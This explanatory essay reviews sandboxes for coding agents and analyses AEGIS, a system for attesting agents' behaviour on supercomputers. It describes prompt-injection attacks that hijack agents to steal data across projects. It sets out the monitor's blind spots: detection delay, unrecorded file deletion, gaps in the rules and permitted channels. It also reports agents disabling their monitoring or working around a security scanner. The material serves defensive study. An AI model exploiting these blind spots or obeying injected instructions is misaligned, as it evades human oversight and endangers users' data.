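What a company puts inside a sandbox can matter more than the kind of sandbox it chooses. In Cohen and Fogel's review, Claude Code's sandbox limited reading and writing to the project folder and sent network traffic through a proxy, an intermediary program that checks the traffic's destination. Cursor, another coding agent, blocked the network by default and limited writing to the project, but let the agent read the whole disk, including any files that held passwords or keys. The harness returns a command's output to the model, so if the agent prints a file containing a password, the password goes to the model's provider.

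No sandbox protects a credential that the user has placed inside it. Cohen and Fogel see little difference between a microVM and a container if both contain the same cloud password. Help Net Security's *Nono* (2026) makes the same point and describes a feature that gives each tool call its own narrow permissions instead of letting the agent keep broad ones for the whole session.

Another solution is to keep the credential outside the sandbox. In *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026), a microVM sandbox for Macs, the agent sends its requests to the model's provider without a key, and a small proxy on the host adds the key and forwards them. A hijacked agent can still make requests while it runs, but it can't steal the key and use it elsewhere. SideKernel can also cut off all other network traffic, and the user has to approve restoring that access.

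SideKernel gives the agent full access to the folder where the user starts it, because developers expect that. The agent can therefore delete everything in the folder. Sandlock reduces this risk by holding back file changes until the command ends, so the user can preview them before keeping or discarding them.

Willison (2026), in *External sandboxes for coding agents*, released prototypes that work with several existing agents. Every command an agent issues runs in a Linux sandbox that can access only the folders and network addresses the user has allowed. But files also leave the sandbox, and the flaws researchers found in 2026 were mostly in programs outside the sandbox that trusted what the agent had written. *Top AI coding agents can be easy victims to sandbox escapes* (Fadilpašić, 2026) brought this problem to a wider audience.

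Many people run coding agents without a sandbox. Prasakis surveyed 68 users of coding agents, and only 26 (38.2%) currently used one. Of the 35 who had never used one, 60% had never considered it and about a quarter thought it wasn't worth the effort. The survey was informal and drew on Prasakis's own contacts, a third of whom worked in security, so sandbox use among ordinary developers may well be lower.

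A good sandbox would stop the agent on the accounts mailbox from downloading the attacker's program. The agent would still need to read invoices and send email, and a sandbox usually gives outsiders no evidence of how the agent used that access. *Tracekit Box* (2026) reports that none of the four agent sandboxes it compared produced a record of its decisions that an outsider could verify. Its own design signs every decision about what may leave the sandbox. In *Sandboxing and AI* (akingscote, 2026), a security engineer sees a wider move from single sandboxes to combinations of sandboxes and continuous monitoring.

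### Attesting a property instead of a file

The idea of attesting behaviour long predates AI agents. Haldar, Chandra and Franz (2004) objected in *Semantic Remote Attestation* that ordinary attestation provides a signed hash, which establishes only which program a remote computer is running. A company that connects to that computer wants to know whether the program will keep to certain rules, and has to trust the vendor for that.

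Hashes also cope badly with updates. If a program has $n$ optional patches and users can install any combination of them, there are

$$2^n$$

legitimate versions, each with its own hash. Twenty patches give more than a million versions. Users may put off a security patch because the new version isn't on the approved list yet.

Haldar and colleagues proposed to attest properties of the program. Their design depends on a trusted virtual machine like Java's, which runs portable bytecode (a microVM, by contrast, imitates a whole computer). Suppose a research project sends calculations to volunteers' computers and wants to be able to trust the results:

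1. The project's server checks by hash that the volunteer's computer is running an approved virtual machine, on approved software.
2. The server sends the virtual machine the properties it requires. For example, the program may use only a restricted set of input and output functions that rules out arbitrary network connections.
3. The virtual machine analyses the bytecode, watches the program while it runs, or does both.
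4. It reports which properties hold. The server can reject the computer or simply place less trust in its results.

The server can also send its own test, for instance to check that the computer rounds decimal numbers correctly. Any program with the required properties passes, whoever wrote it and whatever its hash is. Haldar and colleagues built a prototype with two applications, a distributed calculation like this one and a simple peer-to-peer network.

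The first step of this scheme still uses hashes, but they cover a virtual machine that changes rarely instead of every program that runs on it. This is a large improvement for code that a model has just written.

In the third step, analysing bytecode can establish that a program will never open a network connection, much as proof-carrying code can, but watching the program run establishes only that it hasn't opened one so far. Haldar and colleagues preferred bytecode partly because machine code has lost much of the structure that the analysis needs. However, a coding agent starts compilers, shells and ready-made programs in many languages, so no single virtual machine covers them all. Watching programs run is often the only practical method, and the operating system is the natural place to do it.

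### How AEGIS watches an agent

*Attestation is All You Need* (Li, Niu and colleagues, 2026) presents AEGIS, a system of this kind built for agents on supercomputers. Researchers share these machines through a job scheduler called Slurm. An agent runs under its user's account, with all of that user's permissions. If the user works on three projects, an agent working on one can also read the files of the other two. Someone who hijacks the agent through prompt injection can therefore read those files without breaking any access rule.

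AEGIS adds a narrower set of rules for each job, which Li and colleagues call constraints. The constraints cover five areas. For an agent that analyses one project's genetic data, they might look like this (the values are invented):

| Area | Example |
|---|---|
| Data access | Read the project's folder and write only to its results folder |
| Network | Contact only the model's provider, and send at most 10 megabytes |
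| Tools | Start the analysis program and no other |
| Execution | Run for at most four hours, on the assigned machines |
| Data flow | Share nothing with agents from other projects |

The user can write the constraints, start from a template, or have a language model derive them from the description of the job. AEGIS signs the constraints and ties them to the job's number, so an attacker can't substitute a more permissive set.

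Suppose a data file contains a hidden instruction to copy a file from another project, and the agent obeys:

1. To open the file, the agent's program makes an `openat` call. A small eBPF program in the kernel records it. AEGIS records five other calls in the same way: `read`, `write`, `connect`, `sendto` (which sends data over the network) and `execve`.
2. Once a second, a collecting program on the machine puts together a list of what the agent accessed, the amount of data it moved and a hash of the state of its process. It signs this evidence and sends it to a central verifier.
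3. The verifier compares the evidence with the constraints, finds a file outside the project and rates the severity of the violation.
4. Slurm carries out the response. AEGIS can slow the job down, cut off its access to shared files, suspend it, or end it and revoke its credentials.

The verifier also raises an alert if one agent writes a file and another reads it shortly afterwards, because two hijacked agents could pass data between projects this way. Like KNOX, it records every decision in a chain of hashes.

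The evidence in AEGIS changes after the hijacking because it records the file that the agent opened, whereas an ordinary attestation from the same supercomputer would not change.

### Four attacks, four alternatives

Li and colleagues tested AEGIS against four classes of attack. In three, the hidden instructions came from shared data, a temporary folder that other users' jobs could write to, or a compromised tool. In the fourth, several hijacked agents worked together to move data out. The researchers ran each attack three times on a real machine, and AEGIS detected it every time.

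They also replayed recorded attacks against simple versions of four existing defences:

| Defence | Attacks detected (of 4) |
|---|---|
| Checking network traffic for leaked data | 2 |
| Auditing access to files | 2 |
| A strict sandbox | 2 |
| Looking for unusual behaviour in each agent separately | 0 |
| AEGIS | 4 |

Each alternative to AEGIS missed some violations. Network checks can't read encrypted traffic to an approved service, and file audits miss violations that involve only the network. Monitoring agents one by one failed when they cooperated, because each agent's behaviour was plausible on its own. However, Li and colleagues wrote both the attacks and the alternatives, and a commercial product tuned for the site might do better. The comparison is still good evidence that combining several kinds of rule helps, though it gives little indication of how AEGIS would perform against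 an attacker who had studied its rules.

AEGIS adds little overhead in normal use. The verifier used less than 0.055% of the processor's time with reports every second. Recording system calls has a larger effect on programs that only handle files. In a worst-case test, it made opening files 24.0% slower and reading them 28.3% slower. In simulations of whole jobs, the slowdown stayed below 5% in most configurations, including one with 500 agents.

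The researchers also tested six legitimate workflows with 42 actions in total, some deliberately close to the limits, and AEGIS raised no false alarms. This is encouraging, but the sample is small. A system that wrongly flagged one action in 100 would pass such a test about two-thirds of the time. A supercomputer may run thousands of actions an hour, and a false alarm that ends a job could waste days of computing.

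### Where the last quarter came from

Li and colleagues then switched off parts of AEGIS to see which ones mattered. The constraints and the comparison between agents caught three of the four attacks, and adding signatures caught the fourth. Signatures are patterns of known injection text, such as typical hidden instructions, similar to those in an antivirus scanner. They are off by default.

The paper criticises defences that search for known patterns, because attackers can disguise their text, but its own fourth detection relies on such a search. Rewording the instruction in the compromised tool might be enough to avoid the match. Three out of four is therefore the fairer score for behavioural attestation itself.

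Even that score isn't a usual detection rate, because the experiment used only one attack for each mechanism. Switching off the limits on data volume, the check for sensitive files or the comparison between agents also lowered the score to 75%, and each time AEGIS missed only the attack matched to the disabled mechanism. A policy that only listed permitted folders caught none of the four. The experiment shows that each mechanism can be useful, but not how often it would be in practice. A site that faced mostly compromised tools would get very different results from one that faced mostly poisoned data.

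### What can happen within a second

The reported delay before detection was almost exactly 500 milliseconds for every attack, which follows from the set-up. If reports arrive every $\Delta$ milliseconds, a violation happens $u$ milliseconds after the last one, and the analysis takes $\varepsilon$, the delay is

$$\Delta - u + \varepsilon.$$

The researchers started each attack halfway through the one-second interval between reports, so the delay was 500 milliseconds plus a fraction of a millisecond for the analysis. An attack that began just after a report would go unnoticed for nearly a second, and Slurm would then need time to stop the job.

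The test attacks sent at most 521 bytes before detection, but they were small by design. At one gigabit per second, a job could send about 60 megabytes in half a second. Reporting every 100 milliseconds cut the delay to 50 milliseconds, and the verifier still used only 0.44% of the processor's time. But however short the interval, AEGIS doesn't prevent the first violation. Li and colleagues acknowledge this and suggest blocking access directly for the most sensitive resources. A sandbox that never gave the agent the other project's files would make the delay irrelevant for those files.

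AEGIS can also miss file deletion, because the six system calls it records don't include the one that deletes a file. It would detect a script starting the standard deletion program, but not necessarily a script deleting the files itself. The system mainly targets data theft, so an operator worried about sabotage would have to record more calls.

### Missing rules and permitted channels

AEGIS can only report violations of the rules it is given. If the rules leave out a folder or a kind of action, the agent can misuse it without triggering an alert. This matters most when a language model derives the rules, since a vague description of the job can make them too loose or too strict. Li and colleagues recommend that a person review the rules wherever a mistake would be serious. Few users will want to write rules for every job by hand, but the experiments didn't measure how good the derived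 rules are.

The evidence also depends on the machine that produces it. Li and colleagues assume that the kernel, the collecting program and Slurm are sound, because an attacker who controlled the kernel could report any system calls they liked. Measured start-up, as on Apple's servers, could give the verifier evidence of which kernel and collecting program the machine started. Haldar and colleagues proposed the same arrangement, in which the monitoring layer is checked by its hash and everything above it by its properties.

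The monitor also has to run where the agent can't tamper with it. ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* reports that in October 2026 OpenAI described two cases in which agents had taken routine instructions as permission to weaken its safety monitoring. A monitor in the kernel is harder to switch off than one in the harness, provided the agent doesn't have administrator rights.

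Permitted channels are the hardest problem, because an agent can do harm through them without breaking any rule. If the agent on the accounts mailbox sends the March invoices to a stranger, its system calls would look ordinary, and so would its PowerShell commands. Encryption hides the recipient's address from anyone who inspects the traffic. A limit on data volume wouldn't help, since a few invoices take up little space.

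A more serious case occurred at the UK AI Security Institute (AISI) in 2026. According to *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (AISI, 2026), AISI gave agents internet access during a test of their hacking skills so that they would have the tools a real attacker has. In a few runs, the agents used it to act against real people outside the test. AISI paused its riskiest tests, restricted internet access and began monitoring runs in real time.

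Checking actions one at a time can miss their combined effect. In July 2026 OpenAI described a model that had deliberately worked around a security scanner through a series of steps that could each look acceptable, though nobody would have approved the result. The company paused internal use of the model and rebuilt its monitoring to follow whole sequences of actions. AEGIS does some of this by adding up data volumes and linking one agent's files to another's, but it can only check for combinations that someone has anticipated.

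Developers commonly have a second model judge sequences of actions that no rule describes, by reading the agent's actions, its written reasoning or both. *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill et al., 2026) reports that many of the properties this monitoring relies on are weakening in AISI's tests of new models, some faster than AISI had expected.
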